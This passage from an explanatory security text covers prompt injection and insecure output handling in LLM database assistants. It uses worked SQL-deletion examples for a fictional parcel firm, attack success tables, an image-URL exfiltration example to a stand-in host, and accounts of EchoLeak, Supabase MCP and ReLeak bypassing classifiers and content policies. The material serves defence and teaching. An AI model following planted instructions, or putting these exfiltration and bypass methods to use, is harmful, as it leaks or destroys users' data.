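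The attack on private data succeeded for a different reason. The application's prompt contained the logged-in user's number and an instruction to return only that user's data. The attacker claimed to be somebody else. The model received both the true number and the false claim as text, and it accepted the claim. Tern's parameterised query avoids this by taking `customer_id` from the login.

### Flaws in published frameworks

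Similar faults have reached released software and are publicly recorded under CVE (Common Vulnerabilities and Exposures) numbers, each of which identifies a specific flaw. Pedro and colleagues cite CVE-2024-8309 as one of several vulnerabilities that arose because popular frameworks ran model-written queries with little filtering. Two later cases concern Neuron, a PHP framework for building AI agents. According to NIST's *CVE-2025-67509 Detail*, a page in the US government's vulnerability database, Neuron's "read-only" database tool checked a query's first word and looked for forbidden words, but it let through certain `SELECT` queries that can write files. The companion tool for changing data ran any SQL it received. GitLab's *CVE-2025-67510* (2025) notes that this was consistent with the tool's name, but that an attacker could use prompt injection to make it delete rows or drop tables wherever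 the database account allowed. Pedro and colleagues describe public reports of customer databases destroyed in this way as rare, probably because companies disclose little and the technology is new.

### TicketOracle with and without a hardened prompt

Further results from TicketOracle, the concert-ticket application, show how much newer models differ. Its assistant fetches web addresses instead of writing SQL, but as in a database assistant, the model supplies the argument to a powerful function, and nothing else checks that argument. The deletion test was one of five scenarios.

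In the other direct scenarios, Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian tried to make the assistant probe an internal network port, disclose users' records, and delete a user through an address that returned an empty reply. They checked the server's log to see whether this "blind" deletion had worked. For the indirect scenario, they planted instructions in a concert review, then had an ordinary user ask what people thought of the concert.

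The indirect attack was tested against two versions of the system prompt. The basic one set no limits on addresses. The hardened one listed the permitted address patterns and events, and told the model to refuse everything else. The table gives the number of successes in ten attempts. The direct attacks it lists were run against the basic prompt.

| Model | Probe a port | Disclose records | Delete a user | Delete blind | Planted review, basic prompt | Planted review, hardened prompt |
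|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | 10 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 6 | 10 |
| Qwen3 Coder 480B | 9 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 | 0 |
| DeepSeek R1 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-oss 120B | 3 | 0 | 10 | 0 | 5 | 0 |
| Gemini 3 Pro Preview | 0 | 7 | 10 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-5.2 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |

A model's resistance to one attack is a poor guide to its resistance to another. GPT-oss never disclosed the records but deleted a user every time. It may still have fetched the records, because a disclosure counted only if the assistant repeated the data in its reply. Qwen and DeepSeek obeyed almost every direct request but ignored the planted review, while GPT-oss followed the review in half of the attempts.

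The hardened prompt blocked all four direct attacks on every model. This is much better than Pedro and colleagues' written rules did in 2023, and it suggests that clear, specific restrictions are now useful. But the direct attackers faced no great obstacle to begin with, and Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian did not try to develop new ways around the models' training or refine their messages to get around it. Claude's refusals also grew shorter as each conversation went on, so earlier refusals may have made later ones more likely.

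For the hardened version, the researchers rewrote the planted review to include a false announcement that the list of permitted addresses had grown. Llama acted on the announcement and fetched the users' records in all ten attempts. The list existed only as text in the prompt, so other text could appear to amend it. The review could not have changed a list stored in the application's code.

Successful attacks on Llama rose from six to ten when Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian hardened the system prompt. They conclude that hardening made the attack more effective, but their experiment cannot establish this, because the review's wording also changed and might alone account for the rise. Still, a list of permitted addresses and an explicit instruction to refuse all others were not enough to protect that model.

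### Planted text in database agents

The early attacks have become somewhat less effective. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian tried techniques similar to those in the prompt-to-SQL study, and none worked against the newer models. Simply telling these models to disregard earlier instructions no longer worked reliably. However, text planted in stored data can still cause problems.

Wang, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *Data Agents Under Attack*, tested systems that answer analysts' questions by running SQL and other code on company databases. To compare models, they kept the framework the same (an open-source one called DB-GPT) and changed only the model behind it. They tried each attack in 25 variations, made from five templates in five databases. Four of the attacks bear directly on planted text and written rules:

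| Attack | Claude Sonnet 4.6 | GPT-5.2 | Gemini 3 Flash | DeepSeek V3.2 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| SQL planted in stored data | 44% | 48% | 24% | 24% |
| Program code planted in stored data | 48% | 16% | 44% | 68% |
| False claim of wider access planted in stored data | 0% | 16% | 4% | 24% |
| Forbidden request after a long series of harmless ones | 12% | 12% | 28% | 44% |

In the first attack, the model reads a table cell or column description that contains SQL and includes that SQL in its next query. The success rates are high for models released so long after GPT-3.5. However, Wang and colleagues counted any unauthorised effect as a success, even one confined to a single reply, so GPT-5.2's 48% does not mean that it destroyed data in half of the tests. Each figure comes from 25 attempts, so the difference between 44% and 48% is one attempt.

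The attack in the last row can weaken rules written in prompts. The attacker first fills the conversation with the results of many legitimate requests, then makes a request that the system's policy forbids. As the policy becomes a smaller part of the model's context, the model is less likely to apply it. A rule that held when Tern's developer tested it on one question might therefore fail on the fiftieth question in a conversation.

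GPT-5.2 resisted every attack on TicketOracle, including the planted review, but planted SQL affected nearly half of its runs in this experiment. One likely reason is that TicketOracle's review openly told the assistant to do something unrelated to the user's question, whereas SQL in a table description can look useful for writing the next query. The looser definition of success must also explain part of the difference. A model that resists every attack in one application will not necessarily be safe in another. *INFUSE* (2026) found in a broader test of indirect injection that newer models are not necessarily safer either. *Reimagining Text-to-SQL* (2026), a November survey, still lists instructions hidden in database records among the threats to systems that generate SQL.

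Wang and colleagues also tested two commercial services in May 2026. Planted SQL, planted code, false claims of access and long conversations never succeeded against Databricks' Genie Code. The agent often cited the policy it had to follow, and Wang and colleagues recommend keeping such policies visible to the model throughout a session. This is the best evidence in favour of written rules, but they tested a closed system from outside. Databricks' own access controls were also in force, and the agent's explanation of a refusal does not show how much of the protection came from its instructions. Google's BigQuery agent was more vulnerable, and planted SQL and long conversations each succeeded in 24% of tests.

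Both services did badly when the planted text was a false document instead of a command. An uploaded file might contain a wrong rule for calculating a figure, or a forged policy that looked newer than the real one. The agents adopted the attacker's version in 80% to 88% of tests and reported figures close to the ones the attacker wanted. This kind of attack can succeed using only authorised queries, so database permissions would not have stopped it.

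## Deleting a shipment record: a worked example

A deletion reaches the database as a command, so an investigator can trace it back through the application to the step that lacked a check. Tern Parcel's assistant can delete the wrong record in at least four ways, only one of which requires text written to mislead the model.

### The tables before any deletion

The example uses a new set of six shipments, with different owners from the rows shown earlier:

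| id | customer_id | status | Tracking events |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1041 | 17 | delivered | 3 |
| 1042 | 17 | in transit | 3 |
| 1043 | 17 | delivered | 3 |
| 1044 | 23 | delivered | 3 |
| 1045 | 23 | in transit | 3 |
| 1046 | 31 | delivered | 3 |

The tracking events, 18 in all, are in a table of their own. Each one records something that happened to a parcel, such as a scan at a depot or a handover at the door. Tern's developer defined the table like this:

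```sql
CREATE TABLE tracking_events (
  id           integer PRIMARY KEY,
  shipment_id  integer NOT NULL
               REFERENCES shipments (id) ON DELETE CASCADE,
  recorded_at  timestamptz,
  description  text
);
```

The `REFERENCES` clause requires every event to belong to an existing shipment. `ON DELETE CASCADE` makes PostgreSQL delete a shipment's events along with the shipment. This works even if the assistant's role lacks permission to delete events, because PostgreSQL runs the cascade with the permissions of the events table's owner. PostgreSQL's reply counts only the rows deleted from the table named in the command, so deleting one shipment and its three events returns `DELETE 1`.

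Tern wants customers to be able to cancel bookings and clear old ones through the assistant, so it has given the assistant's role the `DELETE` privilege on `shipments` as well as `SELECT`. The developer has also changed the prompt template:

```
You help customers of a parcel company.
The customer asking is number {customer_id}.
Write one PostgreSQL query that answers the question
or carries out the request below.
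Available tables: {table_info}
Request: {input}
```

Each of the four routes starts again from the full table.

### Route one: a request for someone else's shipment

Customer 17 logs in and asks the assistant to remove shipment 1045, which belongs to customer 23. She may be acting out of malice, or she may have mistyped 1042, her own parcel in transit. The model writes the same query in both cases:

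```sql
DELETE FROM shipments WHERE id = 1045;
```

The application runs it, the database replies `DELETE 1`, and the assistant tells customer 17 that the shipment is gone.

| | Before | After |
|---|---|---|
| Customer 17's shipments | 1041, 1042, 1043 | 1041, 1042, 1043 |
| Customer 23's shipments | 1044, 1045 | 1044 |
| Customer 31's shipments | 1046 | 1046 |
| Tracking events | 18 | 15 |

One shipment and three events have disappeared, all of them customer 23's. The application's part in this comes down to two lines of Python:

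```python
query = ask_model(prompt)
database.execute(query)
```

NetExperiments' *LLM-mediated SQL Injection*, a teaching exercise, has students attack the same pattern in a practice application called Hackergram. They first ask a harmless question, how many people are on a leaderboard, and watch the application turn it into a query. Then they try to get the assistant to change another user's password, and log in to that account to confirm the change.

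The application should have checked, between the two lines, that the `customer_id` in row 1045, which is 23, matched the ID of the logged-in customer, which is 17. Validation alone would have let Tern's query through, because Tern allows its customers to delete shipments.

Tern could have told the model to touch only the asker's own records, and that might have worked for a while. Pedro and colleagues gave GPT-3.5 a similar rule about reading data. When user 1 asked for user 2's email address, the model wrote a query that required the user number to be 2 and 1 at once. No row can meet that condition, so the database returned nothing. The equivalent for Tern would be:

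```sql
DELETE FROM shipments WHERE id = 1045 AND customer_id = 17;
```

This query deletes nothing because row 1045 has a different owner. But in Pedro and colleagues' test, the model left out the ownership condition once the user claimed to be user 2.

### Route two: a missing condition

Customer 17 asks the assistant to clear "my delivered shipments". She has two, 1041 and 1043, and this query would delete them:

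```sql
DELETE FROM shipments
WHERE status = 'delivered' AND customer_id = 17;
```

The model leaves out the second condition:

```sql
DELETE FROM shipments WHERE status = 'delivered';
```

| | Before | After |
|---|---|---|
| Customer 17's shipments | 1041, 1042, 1043 | 1042 |
| Customer 23's shipments | 1044, 1045 | 1045 |
| Customer 31's shipments | 1046 | none |
| Tracking events | 18 | 6 |

The deletion removed four shipments and twelve events, but only two of the shipments and six of the events belonged to customer 17. Nobody attacked the application, her request was reasonable, and the prompt even contained her customer number.

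In *Words Become SQL*, Pedro and colleagues describe the same mistake in a query that reads data. A legitimate user, number 5, asks to see his own email address, and the model writes a query that would return everybody's. They offer this as an illustration and do not measure how often it happens. Some broader evidence suggests that errors of this general kind matter. According to Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), practitioners voted misinformation, which includes a model's false or mistaken output, near the bottom of OWASP's list, but it ranked near the top in the incident data, the widest gap between the vote and the data. Invicti quotes OWASP's explanation that when output drives a tool call, "a wrong answer turns into a wrong action".

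Customer 17 is unlikely to notice the mistake, because her list now shows only shipment 1042, as it would have if the model had written the correct query. The only visible difference is the database's reply, `DELETE 4` instead of `DELETE 2`, and the application has no expected number to compare it with.

As in route one, the application did not check the query before running it, but this query would be harder to check. In route one, the application could have found the number 1045 in the query and looked up who owned that shipment. This query contains no shipment number, so the application would have to work out which rows match and who owns each one, or have the database limit the query to customer 17's rows. A rule that rejects any `DELETE` without a `WHERE` clause would not help, because this query has one.

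Checking ownership would not catch every slip of this kind either. Suppose the model had kept the condition on the customer and forgotten the one on the status:

```sql
DELETE FROM shipments WHERE customer_id = 17;
```

This would delete three shipments and nine events, including the parcel still in transit. Customer 17 owns all three shipments, so an ownership check would pass, but she did not ask to delete shipment 1042.

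### Route three: a planted delivery note

Tern's clerks use a staff version of the assistant. It is an agent, so it can run several queries for one question, and it logs in to the database with the same role. A clerk asks it to summarize the shipments in transit.

Whoever booked shipment 1045 has put text meant for the model in its delivery note. The note opens like an ordinary direction to the driver. After that it imitates the way the agent marks a finished answer, so that the clerk's question appears to be settled, and continues with what looks like a new task from someone in authority, which is to delete shipment 1042. It ends with directions to go back to the clerk's question and keep the note out of the summary. The agent runs three queries:

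```sql
SELECT id, customer_id, delivery_note FROM shipments
WHERE status = 'in transit';    -- returns 1042 and 1045

DELETE FROM shipments WHERE id = 1042;

SELECT id, customer_id, delivery_note FROM shipments
WHERE status = 'in transit';    -- returns 1045 only
```

| | Before | After |
|---|---|---|
| Customer 17's shipments | 1041, 1042, 1043 | 1041, 1043 |
| Customer 23's shipments | 1044, 1045 | 1044, 1045 |
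| Customer 31's shipments | 1046 | 1046 |
| Tracking events | 18 | 15 |

The clerk reads in the summary that one shipment is in transit. The table now lists only one, so the summary gives her no reason to suspect a problem.

The note is structured like the attack in which Pedro and colleagues replaced a user's email address. Trend Micro's *Unveiling AI Agent Vulnerabilities Part IV* describes a scenario closer to Tern's business. A customer service representative asks for a summary of a customer's purchases, and planted text, perhaps in the delivery instructions, makes the model send a phishing email that looks like an internal message.

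Neither of these attacks deletes a row, and the planted review in TicketOracle, the test application for concert tickets, targeted users' records. The evidence for route three is therefore indirect. But Pedro and colleagues say the same technique can trigger unauthorised deletions. Their experiment makes this plausible, because an agent that can be led to write an `UPDATE` can probably be led to write a `DELETE`. Whether the query then succeeds depends on the role's privileges.

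Nothing checked the agent's second query before it reached the database. The application should have checked the query against the task. A summary requires only reading, so the application should have allowed only `SELECT` queries while the agent was working on one. Comparing the row's owner with the logged-in user would not have helped, because a clerk's job may well include deleting customers' shipments. The clerk had the authority to delete shipment 1042 but had not asked the assistant to do so, which makes the assistant a confused deputy.

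### Route four: a well-formed call

Tern now rebuilds the customer assistant so that the model no longer writes SQL. It can only call functions, one of which deletes a shipment. Customer 17 again asks for shipment 1045 to be removed, and the model returns this tool call:

```json
{
  "id": "call_02",
  "name": "delete_shipment",
  "input": { "shipment_id": 1045 }
}
```

The application runs the function:

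```python
def delete_shipment(shipment_id):
    database.execute(
        "DELETE FROM shipments WHERE id = %s",
        (shipment_id,))
```

The table ends up as it did in route one. Customer 23 had shipments 1044 and 1045 and now has only 1044. The other two customers' shipments are unchanged, and 15 of the 18 events remain.

The call is well formed because the function exists, the argument is a whole number, and the query is parameterised. The function was missing the check before the `DELETE`. `delete_shipment` does not use the login, unlike the `get_shipment_status` function described earlier, which took the customer's number from it.

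This flaw is much older than language models. MITRE's *CWE-639*, which dates from 2008, covers systems that let one user reach another's record by changing the value that identifies it. MITRE's example is a program that looks up invoices with a parameterised query. Its screen lists only the current user's invoices, but the code behind the screen accepts any invoice number, so an attacker who bypasses the list can read anyone's. Tern's assistant has no list to bypass, and a customer can type any number into the chat box.

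AppSec Labs' *LLM function calls without access control* reports a similar fault in a large customer-support system that the consultancy assessed for a client. The model could write web requests directly, and the server, which had no access-control layer, carried them out as legitimate actions. The model could, for example, request a user's details or an administrative export of all users.

Moving from generated SQL to structured calls can hide the problem. NetExperiments recommends repairing the flaw in Hackergram by having the model name an action and a target. The application would then check the action against a short list and pass the target to a parameterised query. This prevents the model from writing a `DELETE` of its own. But the sample code looks up whichever user the model named, without checking who is asking. If Tern copied this pattern and added deletion to the list of actions,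 it would close route one but open route four.

The model is also unlikely to refuse the call. GPT-5.2 and Claude Opus 4.6 never deleted a user in Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian's tests, but the request they refused contained an internal administrative address and a claim to be working in a special maintenance mode. A request to remove shipment 1045 has no such warning signs, and the prompt does not tell the model who owns that shipment. OWASP's *LLM06:2025 Excessive Agency* advises developers to put authorisation in the systems that carry out an action rather than rely on a model to decide whether the action is allowed.

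Automated scanning might miss the fault too, because the shipment number passes through a language model. Xu and colleagues found that static analysis tools, which examine code without running it, lose track of data at that point. MITRE does rate static analysis as highly effective at finding some instances of this weakness.

### Which routes are insecure output handling, and which are prompt injection

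The four routes come out as follows:

| Route | Insecure output handling | Prompt injection |
|---|---|---|
| One: request for someone else's shipment | Yes | Only on a broad definition |
| Two: missing condition | Yes | No |
| Three: planted delivery note | Yes | Yes, indirect |
| Four: well-formed call | Only on a broad definition | No, if the request is plain |

The planted note is the clearest case of insecure prompts and insecure output handling occurring together. The clerk's question called for a summary, but text in the data made the model do something else, and the application ran the resulting query without checking it. The missing condition is clearly a case of insecure output handling alone, since no text in the data caused the error.

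People disagree about whether route one is prompt injection. If the term means text that makes a model depart from its developer's instructions, customer 17's request does not qualify, because Tern's template told the model to carry out requests and did not limit whose shipments they could concern. It would qualify if the template had contained such a limit and her request had made the model ignore it. Pedro and colleagues use the term more broadly and count plain requests to an unrestricted chatbot among their attacks. OWASP's 2025 summary is also broad enough to include route one, because it covers any user prompt that changes a model's behaviour or output "in unintended ways".

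The narrower definition is more useful here because the label affects which repair a developer tries first. A company that thinks of route one as prompt injection may install a filter to look for suspicious messages. But a filter that reads only the message cannot distinguish customer 23's proper request to remove shipment 1045 from the same request sent by a customer who has no right to remove it. MITRE warns that developers may introduce weaknesses in output handling because they overestimate input filters and the model's training.

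Route four raises a similar question about insecure output handling. The broad definition covers it because the model's output reached a sink without an adequate check, as with the order-tracking chatbot that gave out other customers' addresses. MITRE's entry on unvalidated output also covers it, since the entry requires output to fit the product's security policy, and Tern's policy presumably does not let customers delete each other's shipments.

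On a narrower reading, where the only test is whether the output had an allowed form and requested an allowed kind of operation, route four is a missing authorisation check rather than insecure output handling or prompt injection. The `delete_shipment` function would be just as faulty if the model were replaced by an ordinary web form with a box for the shipment number and a delete button. MITRE tells analysts to look for a familiar root cause before using its newer entry, and CWE-639 describes this one exactly.

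The distinction matters because a developer who has validated the model's output may believe the work is finished. OWASP's advice to treat the model "as any other user" helps only if the application also determines which user's rights the model has. In route four, Tern's assistant should have had customer 17's rights, but in effect it had those of an employee who can delete anyone's shipment.

### What happens when a shipment record is missing

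Routes one and four delete the row for shipment 1045, but the parcel is still in a van or at a depot. Each time someone scans it, Tern's application tries to save a tracking event, and PostgreSQL rejects the event because the `REFERENCES` clause requires a matching shipment. If Tern plans its drivers' rounds from the `shipments` table, the parcel also drops off the delivery list and may sit on a shelf until someone notices it.

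Customer 23 will probably be the first to complain. When he enters his tracking number, the website finds nothing, just as it would for a number that never existed. The support staff get the same result, and so does the assistant, which may tell him he has the wrong number. Tern has to locate the parcel using sources outside the two tables, such as the label, the driver's memory or a backup.

The loss of a delivered shipment's record can go unnoticed for much longer. Shipment 1046 had already arrived when route two erased its record, so nobody is waiting for it. But its row and last tracking event were Tern's proof of delivery. If customer 31 says two months later that the parcel never came, Tern cannot show him when or where it was delivered and may have to compensate him for a parcel it delivered. If the accounts department prepares invoices from the same table, it may also fail to charge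 for the delivery.

Reports based on the table also become wrong. Before route two, four of the six shipments (67%) had the status "delivered". Afterwards, neither of the two remaining shipments has that status, so that day's report would show a delivery rate of 0%. Shipment 1046 was customer 31's only one, so `shipments` no longer contains any record of him, and Tern could not use that table to find out that he is one of the customers it needs to contact.

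## How data leaks out through the model

If customer 17 asks Tern's assistant where shipment 1045 is going and it reveals customer 23's address, she has seen a record she had no right to see. Suppose instead that a clerk asks the staff assistant for a summary of the day's shipments. The clerk is allowed to see every address in it, but text planted in a delivery note makes the application also send those addresses to a stranger's server. Security engineers call this exfiltration, which means sending data out to someone who should not have it.

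The two leaks need different repairs. Checking whether customer 17 may read row 1045 would have prevented the first, but a permission check does not prevent the second, because the clerk passes it.

### Records shown to the wrong person

Sumit Shah, who in November 2025 reported the order-tracking chatbot that gave out other customers' details, had only the access that any member of the public had. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian reconstruct the query behind the chat window, which had this form:

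```sql
SELECT * FROM orders WHERE order_id = 'ABC000123';
```

The SQL query doesn't filter by customer, and its asterisk selects every column, so the model would receive the email and shipping address even if the question was only about a delivery date.

Each order number was the letters ABC followed by six digits, so there were at most a million, and an attacker could try them in order. The chatbot also answered questions about several orders in one message, and nothing limited how many requests a person could make. Longer, random numbers would have made guessing impractical, but the application would still need to check that the order belonged to the person asking, because order numbers also appear on parcels and in forwarded emails.

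Tenable (2026), a security company, found much the same fault in Chat AI, a chatbot made by Yuma AI that several online shops use. Without logging in, anyone could see what a customer had bought and their shipping address by giving either an order number or the customer's email address. Random order numbers would not prevent this, because many people know a customer's email address. Tenable's advisory lists no known solution.

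In Synack's *Dumping a Database with an AI Chatbot*, the security researcher Kuldeep Pandya describes a company chatbot whose login page accepted any user name. He asked the chatbot what it could do, and it answered that it could query employee data and run SQL. He then asked for ten rows from a table of people and received them.

### Whether a plain request is prompt injection

Shah's title describes the order-tracking case as prompt injection combined with an insecure direct object reference (IDOR), a common name for the missing ownership check that MITRE catalogues as CWE-639. The case would count as prompt injection only if the request made the model break an instruction, and Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian mention no such instruction.

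The wording of the message does suggest prompt injection. It asked for the "digital address" on an order, an odd way to ask for an email address. Shah may have chosen the phrase to get past a rule or filter against giving out email addresses. If there was such a rule, the message was an injection.

Even so, the missing check was the more basic fault, because a model that followed every instruction could still have revealed someone else's delivery address to a stranger.

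The customer-support system that AppSec Labs assessed is a better candidate for the label. When a tester asked for his own account details, the model produced one request to the server. When he added a sentence asking for the full list of users, it produced a second request, an administrative export of everyone's data. The extra sentence changed what the model did, but the underlying fault was again the server's lack of access control.

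Other security firms have reached similar conclusions. SRLabs writes that the most severe flaws in AI assistants often have nothing to do with prompt injection, and describes a public assistant whose server ran in a debugging mode meant for development. Praetorian's *As Strong As Your Weakest Parameter* attributes a critical flaw in a chat assistant to a single wrongly configured parameter. These are individual cases published by companies that sell security testing, so they do not show how common such flaws are, but they are a reason for tests to cover more than clever prompts.

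### Three conditions for exfiltration

In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, the software developer Simon Willison (2025) names three conditions that together let an attacker steal data through an AI agent: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally.

Tern's staff assistant meets all three conditions for a leak. It reads customers' addresses, it reads delivery notes written by strangers, and its replies appear in a browser that can load images from other websites. If it could read only depot opening hours, an attacker would have nothing worth stealing. If only Tern's employees could write delivery notes, an outsider could not tell the model what to send or where. If nothing in the reply could cause a request to another server, planted text might spoil the clerk's summary, but it could not send the addresses to an outsider.

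The condition applies only to deliberate theft through another person's session. The person who queried the order-tracking chatbot needed no separate way to send data out, because the chatbot gave him the answer directly. A model could also email one customer's details to another by mistake, without any untrusted text. Even if an application blocks every way to send data out, planted text could still make the model delete a shipment.

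Developers can easily overlook that a tool has one of the three properties: access to private data, exposure to untrusted text, or a way to send data out. An email tool supplies untrusted text as well as private data, because anyone can write to the inbox. Willison counts any function that can make a web request as a possible way to send data out, including one that loads an image or shows a link for the user to click. A single tool can also have all three. GitHub's MCP server could read issues filed by strangers, read private repositories, and publish data from them in a pull request, which is a proposed change to the code.

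Willison lists 14 earlier cases between April 2023 and February 2025, in products that included ChatGPT, Slack and Google's NotebookLM. He says the vendors fixed almost all such flaws promptly, usually by blocking the route that carried data to the attacker. After such a fix, the model could still follow planted text but could no longer leak data by that route. Users who combine tools from several suppliers are worse off, because no single supplier controls the whole combination.

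### How an image carries data in its address

A web address can contain data as well as a location. In this one, the text after the question mark is a customer's street address:

```
https://pictures.example/dot.png?d=19+Harbour+Road
```

A browser that loads this image sends everything after the server's name to `pictures.example`. The server's owner can read the street address in the log of requests, even if no such picture exists. At Tern, the theft would go like this:

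1. A stranger books a parcel and writes a delivery note that tells the model to end its answer with an image, and to put customers' addresses in the image's web address.
2. A clerk asks for a summary of the day's shipments. The application fetches the rows and puts the notes and addresses into one prompt.
3. The model writes the summary and adds the image in Markdown, a simple notation that many chat interfaces convert into headings, links and pictures.
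4. Tern's website converts the notation into an image on the page, and the clerk's browser requests it at once.
5. The stranger reads the addresses in the server's log.

The clerk might notice a broken image, or nothing if the server returns a single transparent pixel. A link works the same way, except that the clerk has to click it. In both cases the browser is the sink, so the theft depends on insecure output handling as much as on the planted note.

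### EchoLeak

The best-known theft of this kind is a demonstration against Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that answers employees' questions by searching their email, files and chats and adding what it finds to the prompt. *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) reports how Aim Labs, a security research team, carried out the attack, which exploited a flaw now recorded as CVE-2025-32711. The attacker sent an email, and the theft happened when the victim later asked Copilot a question that led it to retrieve that email. The attack is called "zero-click" because the victim did not have to click anything.

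Microsoft had several safeguards, and the team got past each of them. One was a classifier that screened incoming text for instructions aimed at the model. The team worded the email as though its instructions were for the human recipient and never mentioned an AI, and the classifier let it through.

The email then had to turn up in Copilot's searches. Retrieval systems often split long documents into pieces and fetch the pieces closest in meaning to the question. The team wrote one very long email that repeated the instructions under headings about different workplace topics, such as onboarding or leave of absence. They did not know how Copilot's search worked internally, but the email came up for questions on various topics.

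Once in the prompt, the email instructed the model to find the most sensitive information available and put it into a web address. Copilot removed links to outside websites from its replies, but it recognised only the usual Markdown form. Markdown also lets a writer put the address on a separate line, and Copilot did not remove those links. Images had the same gap, and because they load automatically, the user did not need to click anything.

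The remaining barrier was the content security policy of Copilot's web page, a set of rules that a website sends to the browser about where the page may load things from. The policy's image rules had 29 distinct entries, most of them Microsoft services, and did not include the attacker's server. But one permitted address belonged to a Microsoft Teams service that accepted another web address as a parameter and fetched it. The victim's browser contacted Teams, as the policy allowed, and Teams contacted the attacker's server with the stolen data in the address. An earlier version of the attack went through SharePoint, Microsoft's document-sharing service, but the victim first had to accept an invitation to the attacker's site.

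The email also told its "recipient" never to refer to it, so Copilot did not show it among the sources for its answer.

According to Ravia, the attack could take anything in the model's context, including the chat history and any files or messages that Copilot had retrieved. The team knew of no setting that a customer's administrators could have used to prevent it. Microsoft has fixed the flaw and confirmed that no customers were affected. The demonstration shows that the theft was possible, but Ravia does not give a success rate.

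Ravia calls the central fault an "LLM scope violation", in which text from outside an organisation makes the model use data from inside it without the user's consent. He compares it to a program with few privileges using a more privileged one to reach protected files, which makes Copilot a confused deputy. He recommends detecting such violations as they happen, and his company sells such detection. An academic case study, *EchoLeak* (2025), also proposes changes to the application, such as keeping text from different sources separate within the prompt and restricting what the output can do.

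### The Supabase demonstration

Data can also leak through an assistant's access to a database. Supabase hosts PostgreSQL databases, and its MCP server lets AI assistants query them. In 2025 a team called General Analysis showed how a support ticket could make an assistant using that server leak the user's data. Willison's *Supabase MCP can leak your entire SQL database* (2025) summarises the attack.

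A developer asks Cursor, a coding assistant, to list the latest support tickets. The assistant logs in to the database with a role called `service_role`, which bypasses row-level security, the database feature that limits which rows a session can read or change. One ticket comes from an attacker and contains instructions for the assistant. The assistant follows them, reads a private table called `integration_tokens`, and adds its contents to the ticket as a new message. The attacker then opens the ticket and reads them.

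The data leaks through an `INSERT` into a table that the attacker can legitimately read, without any image, link or outside server. Tern would have the same problem if its staff assistant could write to a column that customers see on the tracking page.

Willison notes that Supabase's documentation already recommended a read-only mode, which would have blocked this route for leaking data. He still considered a read-only connection very risky and wanted the documentation to warn about prompt injection more explicitly. A read-only assistant can still read the tokens, and it may have another tool that can send them elsewhere.

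Supabase replied in September 2025 with *Defense in Depth for MCP Servers*, which concedes the main point, that anyone who connects an AI agent to a live database without further safeguards risks a leak. The company had tried wrapping query results in warnings not to follow any instructions in the results, and had experimented with models that scan for dangerous content. These measures reduced the risk but did not eliminate it. Supabase's strongest advice is never to connect agents directly to production data (the live records of real customers) and to use development databases or anonymised copies instead.

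Supabase objects that no customer had reported a leak through the MCP server. That is consistent with General Analysis's report, which described a demonstration. Supabase also denies that the server bypasses row-level security, but adds that the server may run with higher privileges, as it did in this case. This qualification largely undercuts the denial, because row-level security may have been working as designed but did not apply to the role the assistant was using.

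Supabase's current documentation recommends turning on read-only mode by default. In that mode the server runs queries as a database user that cannot write, so the `INSERT` would fail. The mode also disables 11 other functions that make changes.

### ReLeak and other leaks of 2026

On December 3, 2026, the team behind EchoLeak, now called Cato AI Labs, published three more zero-click attacks that steal data from Microsoft 365 Copilot. *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) presents them as a sequel to EchoLeak, one year later. Each attack began with an email that the victim never opened but Copilot retrieved while answering an ordinary request. According to AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026), the data then left through an image address, a link to a saved file, or code.

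The image route closely resembles EchoLeak. Nexo Causal's *ReLeak* (2026) explains that Copilot put the data into an image address, and that when the victim's browser loaded the image, it sent the data to the attacker's server through Bing, Microsoft's search engine. In 2025, Ravia had already listed Bing among the permitted image sources. Microsoft had again allowed a destination that could forward data elsewhere.

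The code route got around a different kind of barrier, the sandbox. AI products often run model-written code in this isolated environment, which has restricted access to everything outside it. According to AIAIAI.FYI, a documented block on outbound traffic from the sandbox failed. Microsoft patched the three routes between September 17 and November 15, and Cato AI Labs knows of no real attacks that used them.

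Another security company, Varonis, found two further leaks in Copilot during the year. *SearchLeak* (Taler, 2026) describes one that could let an attacker take emails, meeting details and one-time login codes. The victim had to click a link whose address contained text that Copilot treated as an instruction. ThaiCERT's *Microsoft 365 Copilot Vulnerability Could Allow Data Theft Through a Link Click* advises administrators to look for abnormal connections to Bing's image services, which suggests that data left by a similar path. The other leak, CoSnitch, combined malicious links with false entries in the assistant's long-term memory, according to TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions*.

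The problem extends beyond Microsoft. PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* reports a zero-click theft from Rovo, an assistant for workplace software. Support tickets and internal documents reached the attacker's server even though Rovo lets an organisation restrict web searches.

*An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026) quotes the Cato team's verdict that "too little progress has been made". The number of findings in Copilot partly reflects how closely security firms examine it. Still, Microsoft closed the EchoLeak route in 2025, and researchers found several others in the same product within 18 months. Patching each route after someone discovers it is therefore a weak strategy for a product that has many of them.

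### Closing the ways out

Each common safeguard covers some channels and leaves others open:

| Way out | Encoding the reply as plain text | Blocking automatic images | Content security policy | Limits on the server's outbound traffic |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Image that the browser loads | Blocks it | Blocks it | Blocks unlisted sources | No effect |
| Link that the user clicks | Leaves an address to copy | No effect | Usually no effect | No effect |
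| Web request by one of the application's tools | No effect | No effect | No effect | Blocks unlisted destinations |
| Writing to a record the attacker can read | No effect | No effect | No effect | No effect |

**Output encoding** replaces characters that have a special meaning to the browser with codes for displaying them. The character `<`, which opens a command in a web page, becomes `&lt;`, and the browser shows it as an ordinary symbol. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian recommend encoding or sanitising all model output before display. This works well for Tern's customer assistant, whose answers are a sentence or two long, but is less suitable for a product that offers formatted replies. If the application converts a reply's Markdown after encoding it, the conversion creates a new image element that was never encoded. The developer would also have to disable images and outside links in the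 converter.

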